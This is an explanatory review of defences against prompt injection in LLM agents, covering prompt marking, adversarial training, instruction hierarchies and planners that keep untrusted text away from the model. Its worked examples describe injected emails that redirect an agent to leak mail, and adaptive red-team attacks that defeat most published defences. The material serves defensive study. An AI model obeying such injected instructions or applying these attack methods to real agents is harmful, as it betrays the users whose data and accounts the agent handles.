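# Enforcing security and privacy policies in LLM agents through prompt structure, context assembly and control flow

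## How an agent assembles its prompts, and where a policy can be bypassed

A large language model (LLM) continues a text by computing which token, a word or piece of a word, is likely to come next. An LLM agent connects such a model to tools, functions that read a mailbox, query a database, send a message or make a payment, and lets the model choose the next tool for a user's task. The organisation that runs the agent, its operator, usually has rules for it. A security policy might forbid payments to accounts the user has not named, and a privacy policy might forbid sharing customer records outside the support team. Operators often write such rules into the text the model receives. That text also contains emails, web pages and files by other people, and the model can act on instructions in any of it.

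Prompt injection, a term from 2022, means text that makes a model follow instructions its operator or user did not give. A direct injection arrives in the user's own message. *Design Patterns for Securing LLM Agents against Prompt Injections* (Beurer-Kellner, Buesser and colleagues, 2025) gives the example of a customer who tries to manipulate a car seller's chatbot into a large discount. An indirect injection arrives in content that the agent reads while it works, so the attacker doesn't need access to the agent, only a way to put text in that content.

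### One turn of the agent loop

*Securing AI Agents with Information-Flow Control* (Costa, Köpf and colleagues at Microsoft, 2025) gives the example of a user who asks an assistant to summarise recent emails on Project X and send the summary to the user's manager. One of the emails comes from an attacker and contains an instruction to send the top email in the mailbox to an outside address.

The orchestrator, the ordinary software around the model, stores the conversation as a list of messages, each with a role. A system message holds the developer's instructions, a user message holds the task, assistant messages hold the model's output, and tool messages hold the results of tool calls. Before each query to the model, the orchestrator serialises this list into one string. The format OpenAI documents for its open-weight gpt-oss models has a separate developer role for what other formats put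 in the system message. In this format, a reserved token opens each message, a header gives the role, a second reserved token separates the header from the content, and a third closes the message. The string ends with the opening of an assistant message, which the model then continues.

For the email task, the model would probably continue with a call to the mail-reading tool. In OpenAI's format, the message header names the function, the body holds the arguments as structured data, and a special stop token marks the end of the call. So far the model has only produced more text. The orchestrator parses it and decides whether to run the call. If it does, it appends the result as a tool message and sends the model the whole string again, which now contains the instructions, the task, the earlier call and the text of every email, including the attacker's. On the second pass through this cycle,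 called the agent loop, the model should produce a call that sends the summary, and on the third a closing message to the user.

Costa and colleagues define the loop formally. Its central part is the planner, a function that takes the latest message and the planner's stored state, and returns an updated state and one of three actions: Query (give the model a message history and a set of tools), MakeCall (run a tool with given arguments) or Finish (answer the user). Their basic planner turns a model output of the form *ToolCall f args* directly into the action *MakeCall f args*, so the software runs whatever tool call the model requests. To enforce a policy, a designer can replace this planner with a stricter one or insert a check before MakeCall takes effect.

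### Why a rule in the prompt is only a request

An operator could add a rule to the system message that forbids sending mail outside the company, but the rule becomes part of the same string as the attacker's email. Hugging Face's *Chat templates*, a guide for developers, describes a chat with all its roles as "still just a sequence of tokens". The rule and the attacker's sentence can only change the probabilities of what the model writes next.

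Developers train models to favour the rule. When instructions conflict, gpt-oss applies an order of precedence set out by OpenAI, with system messages at the top and tool messages at the bottom. But this is learned behaviour, and if it fails, nothing else in the basic loop stops the call. Even a low failure rate per attempt offers limited protection if the attacker can send a hundred emails. *Adaptive Evaluation of Out-of-Band Defenses Against Prompt Injection in LLM Agents* (Narisetty, Kore and colleagues, 2026) cites Anthropic's figures for Claude Opus 4.5, a model since superseded. In coding environments, an attacker who adapted to the model succeeded 4.7% of the time with one attempt, 33.6% with ten and 63.0% with a hundred.

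Databases had a comparable problem, and developers found a real fix for it. Applications query databases in a language called SQL. If an application pastes a visitor's input into the text of a command, the visitor can type characters that end the intended value and begin a new command, which is called SQL injection. A parameterised query prevents this. The application first supplies the command with placeholders, which fixes its structure, and then binds the visitor's input to them. The input can only fill a placeholder, whatever it contains. The method depends on SQL having a grammar that lets a parser tell where code ends and data begins.

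A prompt has no equivalent, because no parser enforces the role markers inside the model, which processes markers and content together to predict the next token. In *Prompt injection is not SQL injection (it may be worse)*, a December 2025 post for the UK's National Cyber Security Centre, David C concludes that developers may never be able to eliminate prompt injection as they can SQL injection. He considers the comparison dangerous because it leads experienced web developers to expect a similar cure. Narisetty and colleagues accept the comparison and group prompt injection with SQL injection and buffer overflows. Both sources conclude that developers have to put the dependable restrictions in software outside the model.

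### Four places where the policy can fail

In the email task, a policy can fail in the structure of the prompt, the choice of context (all the text the model receives at one step), the choice of the next action, or the arguments of that action.

Prompt structure fails when the model treats part of a tool message as if the user had written it. The orchestrator correctly labelled the attacker's email as the output of the mail tool, but the model still followed the instruction in it. Clearer marking can make this happen less often.

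The orchestrator also put the full text of every email into the context the model would use to pick its next call. It could have kept the emails in memory and given the planner only a name for them. Costa and colleagues show that this is enough for some tasks. To forward the top three emails to a colleague, for example, a planner can refer to the emails by name, and the model never receives their text. Summarizing the emails does require a model to read them, but that can be a second model without tools, which is known as the dual-model design. The choice of context also affects privacy, because a model cannot repeat a salary letter that never entered its context.

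If the attacker's text reaches the planner, the model may request a tool call that isn't part of the task, such as sending the top email to a stranger. *CounterSteer* (2026) classes this as tool hijack, the most severe outcome it measures. An orchestrator that had fixed the sequence of calls before reading any email would reject the extra call.

Fixing the sequence of tool calls does not protect their arguments. Beurer-Kellner and colleagues describe an assistant that must send the day's schedule to the user's boss. If the calls and the recipient are fixed in advance, an injection in the calendar cannot add a call, but it can still change the body of the message arbitrarily. *CounterSteer* counts an attack in which the attacker chooses the content of an argument to a legitimate tool as a compromise in its own right. Dongol (2026), in *On the Relative Security of Prompt Injection*, similarly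 distinguishes an injection that adds a call from one that corrupts a value the plan uses. In the Project X task, the recipient is easy to protect because the user specified it, but the body is much harder because a summary has to depend on the emails. No rule can both allow that dependence and guarantee that the attacker's email does not influence what the manager reads.

### The confused deputy

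The agent in this example had permission to read and send mail, and it used both permissions for the wrong person. Security researchers call this the confused deputy, a term that goes back to a compiler on a shared computer system. Hardy's *The Confused Deputy* describes the system, which belonged to Tymshare, a company that rented out computing time. Users could name a file to receive the compiler's debugging output. According to UT Austin's lecture slides of the same title, the compiler also had permission to update the system's billing file, which ordinary users could not touch. When a user named the billing file for the debugging output, the operating system confirmed that the compiler could write to that file and let it overwrite the bills.

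The access check worked as designed, but it checked the compiler's authority, and a user without that authority chose the file. An agent that sends mail on an attacker's instruction is in the same position. *Kairos* (2026) describes the agent as serving the attacker while staying within the authority it was granted. Ordinary permissions on the mail tool therefore do not help. David C adds that developers can repair a classical confused deputy, but an LLM is "inherently confusable", so designers should limit the harm that confusion can cause.

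Such limits mostly have to protect integrity and confidentiality. Integrity means that untrusted content does not determine consequential actions. Untrusted content is any text that someone other than the operator or user could have written or altered, and consequential actions are tool calls with effects that matter, such as sending, paying, deleting or publishing. Confidentiality means that data reaches only those allowed to read it. The attack on the mailbox violates both, but an agent can violate one without the other. An injection that deletes the user's mail breaks integrity but reveals nothing. A rule that limits who may receive each email would stop the leak to the outside address, but Costa and colleagues point out that such rules do not stop the injection itself. The attacker could still make the agent send unwanted messages to people entitled to the contents. An agent can also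 breach confidentiality without an attacker, by misreading what the user wanted.

### What the attacker controls and sees

Claims about a defence depend on its threat model, which is what its designers assume about the attacker. In a common threat model, Costa and colleagues trust the user's messages and the agent's configuration, which includes the model, the system message and the tool descriptions. The attacker can alter data that tools fetch from untrusted sources, but does not see the queries to the model or its responses. The attacker can also observe the effects of some tool calls. Even a web search may show up in a website's visitor statistics. Narisetty and colleagues further assume that the attacker knows the defence and can design attacks against it.

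Trusting the model here means assuming only that the attacker has not tampered with it, not that it will resist an injection. *Capability Gates Are Not Authorization* (2026) places the model outside the trust boundary, and *Treating the Model as an Untrusted Component* (2026) includes an attacker whose injected instructions the model always follows. That second assumption is useful for design because a defence that works under it does not depend on the model's training. The design instead relies on trusting the component that checks calls, its policy, the tools' code, and the channel through which a user approves actions.

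Descriptions of what the attacker sees also vary. Dongol distinguishes an attacker who sees the content and order of the messages that reach them, one who also sees when each step happens, and one who also learns which requests the software refused, perhaps from an error message. A refusal or a delay can reveal something about the user's data, so a defence that is secure against the first attacker may still leak to the others.

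The weakest common assumption is probably that the user's message is trustworthy. When a user copies a paragraph from a website into the chat and asks the assistant to deal with it, the orchestrator labels the website author's text as the user's own, and any defence that relies on the label gives that text the user's authority. Beurer-Kellner and colleagues note that fixing the plan in advance gives no protection here, because the injected text is already present when the model makes the plan. Narisetty and colleagues regard the initial assignment of origin as under-specified in every system they surveyed. An interface could mark pasted text as foreign, but it would often have to guess, since users also paste in their own notes.

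### Defences inside the model and around it

The component that decides whether a proposed tool call may run has a precedent in the reference monitor, described in *Computer Security Technology Planning Study* (Anderson, 1972). The monitor checks every access against a policy. The system must always invoke it, it must be tamper-proof, and it must be small enough for people to verify. In an agent, it belongs between the model's proposed calls and the software that runs the tools, where *ToolFence* (2026) puts its trusted controller.

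A monitor that checks outgoing mail but not requests for web pages fails the first requirement, because an injection can make the agent put private data into a web address. A policy stored in a file that the agent can edit fails the second. Using another LLM to judge each call would have difficulty meeting the third, because nobody can verify that LLM's behaviour over all inputs. Narisetty and colleagues add that such a judge is also open to injection.

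Narisetty and colleagues call defences in-band if they work on the model or on its input and output, and out-of-band if they control its actions from outside. Training a model to resist injections and marking untrusted text in the prompt are both in-band, while a monitor on tool calls is out-of-band. Beurer-Kellner and colleagues instead sort defences into model, user and system levels. User-level defences require users to confirm sensitive actions, but tired users may approve unsafe ones. Beurer-Kellner and colleagues count filters that scan text for injections as system-level because they are separate components, while Narisetty and colleagues count them as in-band. The in-band label is more informative for enforcement, since such a filter still depends on a statistical judgement about text that the attacker wrote.

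The evidence favours putting the final decision outside the model. Narisetty and colleagues report that Nasr and colleagues designed attacks against each of twelve published in-band defences and succeeded more than 90% of the time against most of them. Narisetty and colleagues also warn that researchers have tested out-of-band defences mainly on fixed sets of attacks, so the comparison is not yet fair. Their paper has not passed peer review, and their company builds out-of-band security tools.

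An outside monitor's usefulness depends on its policy, and the obvious policy is too strict for the email task. Beurer-Kellner and colleagues propose as a guiding principle that once an agent has taken in untrusted input, that input must be unable to trigger a consequential action. The simplest way to enforce this is to withdraw the sending tool as soon as the agent reads an email, but that blocks the summary to the manager as well as the attacker's message. Even a monitor that denies every call meets Dongol's definition of security, so designers have to check separately whether the agent can still do its job.

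## Marking trusted and untrusted text inside the prompt

A model that summarises the Project X emails has to read the attacker's text together with the instruction to summarise it. Developers can at least mark which text is trusted and which is not. Some methods change only the input, by adding symbols around the untrusted text or altering the text itself. Others also train the model to treat the marks as a boundary. All of these are in-band defences, so the model still chooses the tool call.

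### Delimiters and spotlighting

The simplest mark is a delimiter, a symbol that the orchestrator puts before and after the untrusted text. The system message names the symbols and tells the model to obey nothing between them. Hines, Lopez and colleagues at Microsoft tested this in *Defending Against Indirect Prompt Injection Attacks With Spotlighting* (2024), using 1,000 synthetic documents, each with an injected instruction to drop the task and answer with a single keyword. When GPT-3.5 Turbo summarised the documents, the attack succeeded about 60% of the time. A warning in the system message barely changed that rate, while delimiters halved it. Hines and colleagues still advise against delimiters, because an attacker who learns the symbols can type them into the document.

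*Defending Against Indirect Prompt Injection Attacks With Spotlighting* recommends marking untrusted text throughout, and calls this family of techniques spotlighting. In one of them, datamarking, the orchestrator replaces every space in the untrusted text with a rare character and explains this in the system message. If the mark is a caret, the phrase "Project X is late" in an email reaches the model as "Project^X^is^late", and any instructions an attacker put in the email are marked the same way. In a summarisation test, datamarking reduced attack success on GPT-3.5 Turbo from about 50% to 3.1%. It did not harm performance on four language benchmarks, though it may not suit inputs such as program code.

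Encoding converts the document into a code such as base64, which the model has to decode as it reads. This reduced the attack success rate in summarisation to 0.0%. GPT-4 handled encoded text about as well as plain text, but GPT-3.5 Turbo made many more mistakes.

Spotlighting doesn't change the model's weights, so it relies on the model to connect the warning with the marks. Google's *Lessons from Defending Gemini Against Indirect Prompt Injections* (2025) describes a version that inserts a marker every eight characters into an email's sender, subject and body. When the researchers varied the settings, however, they found that the markers worked mainly by breaking up the tokens of the injected instruction, which made the model less likely to interpret it as an instruction. They therefore expected the defence to work poorly against attacks in some languages.

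### Training a separate data channel

An attacker can type any delimiter made of ordinary characters. *StruQ* (Chen, Piet and colleagues, 2024) proposes that applications supply the instruction and the data as separate inputs. A front-end joins them with reserved tokens and deletes any string in the data that would become one of those tokens. It repeats the deletion until the text stops changing, because removing one string can bring together the halves of another. Ordinary software can guarantee this separation in the prompt, much as a database guarantees the structure of a parameterised query, but whether the model respects the boundary still depends on training.

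For that training, StruQ used models that could continue text but had not yet learned to follow instructions. Half of the training examples were normal. In the other half, the researchers added a misplaced instruction to the data part of each example that had one, sometimes after a fake answer and imitation delimiters. The target response always ignored the misplaced instruction. An attack that combined a fake answer with the real delimiters succeeded 96% of the time against an undefended Llama model with 7 billion parameters, but never against the StruQ version, whose answers were of about the same quality.

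Optimised attacks succeeded more often. Greedy Coordinate Gradient (GCG) uses a model's gradients to search for a string that triggers the output the attacker wants. It succeeded against the StruQ version of Llama 58% of the time, compared with 97% without the defence. StruQ's training covered only simple injections, and the protection did not fully carry over to injections tailored to each task.

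SecAlign, by some of the same researchers, trains on pairs of responses. Chen, Zharmagambetov and colleagues (2025), in *Meta-SecAlign*, give the example of a user who wants a recipe for a dish named in the data. The data contains the word "omelette" and an injected question about the origins of yoga. The preferred response, w, is the recipe, and the rejected response, l, answers the question. Training minimises

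loss = −log σ(β · [log(π(w)/π₀(w)) − log(π(l)/π₀(l))])

π is the probability that the model in training assigns to a response, and π₀ is the probability that the original model assigned to it. The function σ maps any number to a value between 0 and 1, and β sets the scale. At the start of training, π equals π₀, so both logarithms are zero and the loss is log 2, about 0.69. The loss falls as the recipe becomes more likely relative to the answer about yoga.

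SecAlign made larger models complete fewer tasks. AgentDojo is a benchmark with 97 user tasks for agents with tools, and it places injections in the tools' results. With no attack, SecAlign reduced the share of tasks that Llama 3.3 70B completed from 59.8% to 6.2%. SecAlign's training examples always put the injected instruction at the end of the data, so the model learned to ignore whichever instruction came last. In an agent's prompt, the last instruction was often the user's request, and the model returned nothing.

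Meta SecAlign puts about half of the injections at the beginning instead. It also uses the original model's answers as training targets, so that the model doesn't shift towards another model's style. Across eight utility benchmarks, the largest loss was 2.7 percentage points. Attack success on AgentDojo fell from 14.7% to 1.9% in tests that also used prompt sandwiching, which repeats the user's request after the untrusted text. The method assumes that the orchestrator has already identified which text to trust, so it doesn't protect against injections in pasted text.

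### Ranking instructions by source

An agent's prompt usually has more than two sources. To rank them, gpt-oss uses an instruction hierarchy, an idea that Wallace and colleagues introduced in 2024. *IH-Challenge* (Guo, Ceron Uribe and colleagues, 2026) gives the full order as system, developer, user and tool, and defines the rule with sets. B starts as the set of all possible responses. For each role, from the highest rank to the lowest, C is the set of responses that its instructions permit. If B and C overlap, the overlap becomes the new B. If they do not, the instructions conflict with a higher rank, and B stays unchanged.

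Suppose the system message in the Project X task forbids mail to outside addresses. The user's request is compatible with this rule, so B then contains only responses that obey the rule and send the summary to the manager. None of these sends an email to the attacker, so the model should ignore the attacker's instruction. Without the operator's rule, a response could both send the summary and forward the top email. Read literally, the definition would then require the model to do both, even though Guo and colleagues describe tool messages as untrusted. StruQ and SecAlign avoid this problem by training the model to ignore every instruction in the data, whether or not it conflicts with other instructions.

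Guo and colleagues taught the ranking with reinforcement learning, in which the model produces responses and training strengthens those that score well. Each exercise combines a simple rule, such as keeping a PIN secret, with a short program that checks the response. A second model writes a message that conflicts with the rule and revises it against the current version of the model being trained, so the attacks get harder as the defence improves. Some exercises contain harmless requests that look forbidden, because a model could otherwise score well by refusing too much.

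This training raised GPT-5 Mini's average robustness across 16 benchmarks from 84.1% to 94.1%. On OpenAI's fixed internal set of agent injections, the share the model resisted rose from 44% to 100%, but on the public benchmark CyberSecEval 2 it rose only from 88% to 91%. The model also became slightly less useful in ordinary chat, where its win rate against an older OpenAI model fell from 71% to 66%.

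Other researchers have changed how a model represents the priority of instructions. Instructional Segment Embedding adds trainable information about priority to the vectors that represent input tokens. FocalLoRA adapts only the attention heads (components that relate tokens to one another) that respond to conflicts between instructions. *Improving Instruction Hierarchy by Learning from Goal-Goal Conflicts* (2026) changes the training examples instead. Its method puts one text-processing instruction in the system message and a competing one in the user message, then swaps them to make a second example. The swap presumably keeps the model from favouring an instruction because of its content.

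### Whether the model recognises the marks

A model can learn to ignore familiar attacks without learning where text came from. Ye, Cui and Hadfield-Menell (2026), in *Prompt Injection as Role Confusion*, examined this with probes, simple classifiers that read a model's internal activations. They wrapped identical passages of web text in the tags of five roles (system, user, reasoning, assistant and tool) and trained the probes to identify the role. Because the passages were the same, the probes could distinguish the roles only by how the tags changed the activations.

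They then applied the probes to a conversation about gardening and found that the style of the text affected the scores more than its tags did. In gpt-oss-20b, passages of the model's own reasoning scored an average probability of 85% for the reasoning role, and 83% when all tags were removed. When the researchers put the entire conversation inside user tags, the passages again scored 85% for the reasoning role and only 2% for the user role.

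This confusion also predicted which attacks would work. Across 1,000 attempts to make agents leak data, the success rate rose from 2% where measured confusion was lowest to 70% where it was highest. In another experiment, Ye and colleagues reworded injected text to keep its argument but remove the style of the role it imitated, and average attack success fell from 61% to 10%.

StruQ's filter stops an attacker from producing a reserved token, but the attacker can still write like a user. Datamarking may help partly because text with a caret between every word no longer resembles a user's message.

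### Attacks designed against the defence

Most of the low attack success rates reported so far were measured using attacks that existed before the defence. Dongol classes spotlighting as a heuristic and points out that benchmarks of known attacks cannot show that no attack succeeds. *The Attacker Moves Second* (Nasr, Carlini and colleagues, 2025) tested twelve defences against attackers who adapt, using the attack most likely to defeat each one.

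Their automated attacks ran in a loop that proposed an injection, tried it on the defended system, scored the result and used that score to improve the next proposal. Depending on the defence, the researchers improved proposals using gradients, reinforcement learning or a genetic search in which a language model suggested changes. More than 500 people also took part in an online attack competition. On a subset of scenarios used to compare the two approaches, the automated search succeeded 69% of the time, while the human participants collectively succeeded in every scenario.

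The table compares the marking defences under fixed and adaptive attacks. The adaptive results come from Nasr and colleagues, except those for the hierarchy training, which Guo and colleagues tested themselves.

| Defence | What developers change | Success of fixed attacks | Success of adaptive attacks |
|---|---|---|---|
| Prompt sandwiching | Input | As low as 1% | Over 95% |
| Spotlighting | Input | As low as 1% | Over 95% |
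| StruQ | Input format and weights | At most 2% for handwritten attacks | Every case tested |
| Meta SecAlign | Input format and weights | 2% | 96% |
| Hierarchy training (GPT-5 Mini) | Weights | 0% on OpenAI's internal set | 11.7% of tasks |

These rates cannot be used to rank the defences, because the tests differed. In the StruQ test, the attacker only had to make the model print a fixed phrase, whereas the Meta SecAlign test used harmful tool calls. Nasr and colleagues describe the version of spotlighting they tested as relying on delimiters, the form that Hines and colleagues had advised against, so the result does not directly measure datamarking or encoding. Nasr and colleagues also gave attackers ample computing power, reasoning that a defence should not depend on attackers having little of it.

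Injection detectors did little better. Nasr and colleagues defeated three of the four they tested more than 90% of the time, and the fourth, PIGuard, 71% of the time. Many of the successful injections read like ordinary workplace notes, so a detector could catch them only by also blocking much harmless text. Another defence, MELON, runs the agent a second time with a neutral request in place of the user's task. If the agent makes the same tool call again, MELON assumes that the tool's output caused it. The automated search defeated MELON 76% of the time without information about how it worked, and 95% with it.

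The hierarchy training held up better, perhaps because its attacks adapted during training. Based on earlier work with image classifiers, Nasr and colleagues expected training on adaptive attacks to give more protection than training on fixed ones. Guo and colleagues paid 127 remote workers to attack GPT-5 Mini on the kinds of rules it had trained on, usually offering a $510 bounty for each combination of model and task type. The workers broke 36.2% of tasks before the training and 11.7% after it. When Guo and colleagues trained an attacking model against the finished defence, the attacker's success rate started low and kept climbing.

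### How repeated attempts add up

The workers made an average of about 52 attempts per task against the trained GPT-5 Mini. Only 0.4% of attempts succeeded, but the workers succeeded at least once on more than a tenth of the tasks.

Narisetty and colleagues cite attack success rates against Claude Opus 4.5 that rise from 4.7% after one attempt to 33.6% after ten and 63.0% after a hundred. If each attempt independently failed with probability 0.953, the chance of at least one success in n attempts would be 1 − 0.953ⁿ, which is about 38% for ten attempts and 99% for a hundred.

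The measured rates are lower, so the attempts are correlated. Easier targets tend to be broken early. The figures imply that, among targets not broken on the first attempt, each further attempt up to the tenth succeeds about 4% of the time. Among those still unbroken after ten, the rate drops to about 0.65% per attempt, but an attacker who makes ninety more attempts still breaks another 29 of the original 100 targets.

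A model's apparent robustness also depends on the test. Chen, Zharmagambetov and colleagues tested commercial models with fixed injection attacks placed in tool results. On AgentDojo, the attacks succeeded 0.2% of the time against GPT-5 and 2.3% against Gemini 3 Pro. On SEP, a benchmark that hides unrelated instructions in ordinary text tasks, the rates were 52.6% and 74.6%, counting a success if any of six variants worked. The commercial services may also include defences outside the model. Both models have successors, so these results are not estimates for current models.

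### Marking as one layer

Many unwanted instructions come from people who have not studied the defence. Hines and colleagues describe accidental injections, in which a model acts on instructions meant for a human reader. For example, a model might forward an attachment because an email asked its recipients to do so. Results for fixed attacks are more relevant here than results for adaptive ones, because nobody is trying to get past the marks. The same applies to attackers who only reuse known injections.

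Training the 70-billion-parameter Meta SecAlign model took only seven hours on eight processors, and the method adds no computation when the agent runs. The training also made the model better at handling instructions as text. The trained model gave a correct paraphrase 78.9% of the time when asked to reword commands without carrying them out, compared with 19.8% for the original.

Narisetty and colleagues accept in-band defences as one layer among several and quote OpenAI's view that injection is "unlikely to ever be fully 'solved'". If a policy must hold on every call, the orchestrator still has to refuse the forbidden requests that get past these defences.

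Adding more defenses inside the prompt does not always help. For the original GPT-5 Mini, Guo and colleagues found that repeating the higher-ranking instruction after the untrusted text made the model more robust with little loss of capability. After hierarchy training, such measures brought smaller gains and larger losses in capability, and some made the model less robust. A second model that checked each response reduced the human attackers' success from 11.7% to 7.1% of tasks. Operators therefore need to retest these measures whenever they change models.

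## Keeping untrusted text out of the planner's context

The orchestrator assembles the text from which the model picks its next tool call, so it can leave the attacker's email out. The model then cannot follow instructions in the email, whereas marking the email or training the model to distrust it still leaves those instructions in the text. The difficulty is that the agent still has to do something useful with the email.

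### Passing results by name

Forwarding an email does not require reading it. Costa and colleagues build on this in what they call a variable-passing planner. The planner stores a message history, h, and a memory, mem, which maps names to values. Its next step depends on the latest message:

- After a user message, the planner adds the message to h and queries the model with h and the list of tools.
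- After a tool returns a result v, the planner creates a fresh name x, adds a tool message to h that contains only x, and stores v in mem under x. Then it queries the model again.
- After the model requests a tool call, the planner goes through the arguments. It keeps each literal value and replaces each name x with mem[x]. It returns MakeCall with the resulting arguments, while h keeps the version with the names.
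- After the model writes a closing answer, the planner returns Finish.

The basic planner has the same four cases, but it adds v itself to h and passes on the model's arguments unchanged.

A name such as #read_emails_0 shows the model which tool produced the value, and so roughly what the value is. The orchestrator can also constrain the model's output so that any name it writes exists in the memory. The orchestrator has to generate the names itself, because a name copied from a web page or an attached file could contain an instruction.

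On its own, this planner can complete only data-independent tasks. Costa and colleagues define a task t by the user's request, the available tools and a set D of possible starting states of the data. For each state d, ⟦t⟧(d) is the set of action sequences that solve the task, leaving out model queries. The task is data independent if

⋂ ⟦t⟧(d) ≠ ∅, taken over all d in D

A task qualifies if at least one fixed sequence of tool calls works in every state. Forwarding the top three emails qualifies if the plan can use names to stand for the results of earlier calls. Completing the tasks due today in a to-do app does not, because the right calls depend on the entries in the list.

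### Hiding only part of a result

Hiding every result also hides harmless facts that would help the model plan. Costa and colleagues' full planner, FIDES, hides results selectively. It uses labels that record who may read a piece of data and who may have influenced it. Trusted data has a lower label than untrusted data, and a single untrusted item makes the whole context untrusted.

For each part of a tool result, FIDES checks whether adding it would raise the label of the context. If so, FIDES stores the part under a new name. If not, and the part is a list or a record, FIDES repeats the check on each item inside. It adds everything else to the history unchanged.

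Suppose an email arrives while the context is still trusted. Mail servers can authenticate the sender's address, and an attacker cannot alter some system-generated timestamps, so an operator might label the address and timestamp as trusted and the subject and body as untrusted. FIDES then gives the model the address and timestamp but replaces the subject and body with placeholder names. The model can pick out the manager's emails by address without reading their contents. If the context were already untrusted, hiding the body would no longer protect the planner's decisions, so FIDES would show the body to the model.

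In one sample run, a user asked the agent to find the channel with the fewest messages in Slack, a workplace messaging service, and add Alice to it. FIDES treated the channel names and messages as untrusted, so the model received only placeholder names for them. It could still tell how many messages each list contained, and it added Alice to the channel whose list was empty. Anyone able to post in the channels could have changed those counts, so a result can influence the planner through its shape, such as the length of a list, even when all its text is hidden.

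Models also guess what they cannot read. In a banking task, the agent had to find the price of a New Year's gift, but the transaction descriptions were hidden. Only one transaction fell on 1 January, and the agent reported its amount. The guess was correct, but a user would probably prefer an agent that said it could not tell.

When a task requires the planner to read a variable's value, FIDES offers a tool called inspect, which puts the value into the context. The context then takes on the variable's label, and a policy may then block consequential actions. *SPIDES* (2026) applies the same design to agents that operate a web browser. In SPIDES, inspecting a variable also narrows the set of websites that may receive information from the context.

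An agent that does not know the policy may inspect a variable too early and lose access to a tool it needs later. In *Optimizing Agent Planning for Security and Autonomy*, Kolluri, Sharma and colleagues (2026) tell the model about the labels and policies. Before their agent inspects a variable, it has to explain why and list the calls it intends to make next. It can also ask the user to endorse the content, which means treating it as trusted. If a harmless email lists ten tasks that each need a protected tool, one endorsement replaces ten approvals, but the user then vouches for everything in the email, including any instruction they overlooked.

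### Giving the reading to a second model

Summarising an email calls for the dual-model design, which Willison proposed in *The Dual LLM pattern for building AI assistants* (2023). A privileged model receives the user's requests and can call tools. A quarantined model reads untrusted content and has no tools, and the design assumes an injection may take control of it. The orchestrator, which Willison calls the controller, passes data between the two models.

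Suppose the user asks for a summary of their latest email. The privileged model instructs the controller to fetch the email and store it as $VAR1, then to have the quarantined model summarise $VAR1. The controller inserts the email into the quarantined model's prompt and stores the summary as $VAR2. It sends the privileged model only a notice that the summary is ready. The privileged model writes a reply containing the name $VAR2, and the controller replaces that name with the summary when it displays the reply.

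The summary needs the same isolation as the email, because a model that has read an injection can repeat it in its output. Willison therefore warns against passing the quarantined model's output to the privileged model unless it is one of a fixed set of categories, which the controller can check first.

He also called his own solution "pretty bad", partly because it makes the software more complicated. A single mistake that lets untrusted text reach the privileged model undoes the protection, such as an orchestrator hiding emails but passing on error messages that quote them.

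Separating planning from reading can also help privacy. *CaMeL offers a promising new direction for mitigating prompt injection attacks* (Willison, 2025) discusses a Google DeepMind system that builds on Willison's pattern. Its planning model receives the user's request but no tool results, so the company that hosts this model never receives the user's mail. Reading is easier than planning, so a smaller model on the user's own computer could do the reading.

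### Two tasks under three planners

Costa and colleagues compare these designs on two tasks: sending someone the top three emails as a Slack message, and sending a summary of them. The policy is that a tool call is safe if the model generated it from trusted inputs. The call that reads the emails always meets this policy, because the context at that point contains only the user's request and the agent's own configuration. The table shows what happens to the call that sends the message.

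| Task | Planner | Calls, in order | Context when the model requests the sending call |
|---|---|---|---|
| Forward | Basic | read_emails; send_message with the text of the emails | Untrusted |
| Forward | Variable-passing | read_emails; send_message with #read_emails_0 | Trusted |
| Forward | With a quarantined model | The same two calls; the second model is not needed | Trusted |
| Summarise | Basic | read_emails; send_message with the planner's own summary | Untrusted |
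| Summarise | Variable-passing | read_emails; inspect; send_message with the planner's own summary | Untrusted |
| Summarise | With a quarantined model | read_emails; query_llm; send_message with #query_llm_0 | Trusted |

Under the basic planner, an injection in any of the three emails could change the recipient or add another call. Variable passing prevents this when the task is to forward the emails, but not when it is to send a summary, because the planner has to read the emails to summarize them, which makes its context untrusted before it sends anything.

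In the last row, the query_llm tool passes a question and some variables to a quarantined model and stores the answer in a new variable. When the planner's model requests the call that sends the summary, it has received the user's request and two variable names. An injection can still change the summary, but it cannot change who receives it or make the agent send a second message.

The policy leaves the arguments of a call unchecked. An email could instruct the quarantined model to return an empty summary, and the agent would send it. Requiring trusted arguments would also block accurate summaries. *SPIDES* instead counts an untrusted variable in the arguments as untrusted influence on the call, and then allows the call only if the recipient is entitled to the information.

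### Holding the answer to a schema

In a third task, the agent has to check whether any of the top three emails requests a meeting and, if so, create a calendar event. The planner needs some information about the emails to choose its next call. Costa and colleagues have it query the quarantined model for a yes-or-no answer and inspect only that answer. If the answer is yes, the planner queries the model for the date, time and participants, which stay in a variable that the planner passes to the calendar tool.

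This is safe only if the answer is restricted to yes or no. A schema formally describes the allowed answers, and constrained decoding enforces it while the model writes. At each step, the software running the model excludes every token that could not continue a valid answer, and the model generates one of the rest. If the schema allows only true and false, an injection may reverse the answer but cannot add other text to it.

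A strict schema can force the quarantined model to invent an answer when the text does not contain one. To address this, *SPA* (2026), a design for agents that keep data between requests, gives the model fixed instructions to use only the supplied inputs. If the model cannot meet the objective, it is instructed to return an explicit failure value where the schema provides one.

FIDES also records the type of an answer in its label. It orders types by how much information they can carry:

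bool ⊑ enum["a", "b", "c"] ⊑ string

Here ⊑ means "carries no more than". A Boolean, with two possible values, carries at most log₂ 2 = 1 bit. An enumeration with three permitted values carries at most log₂ 3, or about 1.58 bits, and a string of unrestricted length has no such limit. A policy can therefore let a consequential action depend on an untrusted Boolean but not on an untrusted string. This is a deliberate exception to the rule that only trusted inputs may shape a call. Costa and colleagues justify it by arguing that a Boolean alone is unlikely to cause an injection.

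In *Preventing Prompt Injection with Type-Directed Privilege Separation* (Jacob, Alghamdi et al., 2025), the quarantined model may pass only integers, decimal numbers, Booleans and choices from a fixed list to the privileged agent. One of the paper's test agents fixes software bugs using reports that anyone can write. The quarantined model reads a report and returns a bug category, the index numbers of suspicious files and the lines to examine. The orchestrator looks up the file names in a list it made beforehand. A planning model that has never received the report then writes several repair plans. A separate quarantined model compares the plans with the report and returns only the number of the best one.

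The privileged agent uses the plan and the list of locations to repair the bug in a clean copy of the code. The attack success rate fell to zero in this test and in tests of a shopping agent and a calendar agent. The design excludes the free text those attacks needed, so the tests mainly confirm that the researchers implemented it correctly.

A long enough integer can encode a whole document, and so can a long list of small integers. Jacob and colleagues cap the length of lists to prevent what they call decoding attacks, but their definition of the integer type has no maximum. A schema that permits only integer scores from 0 to 10 limits each answer to about 3.5 bits.

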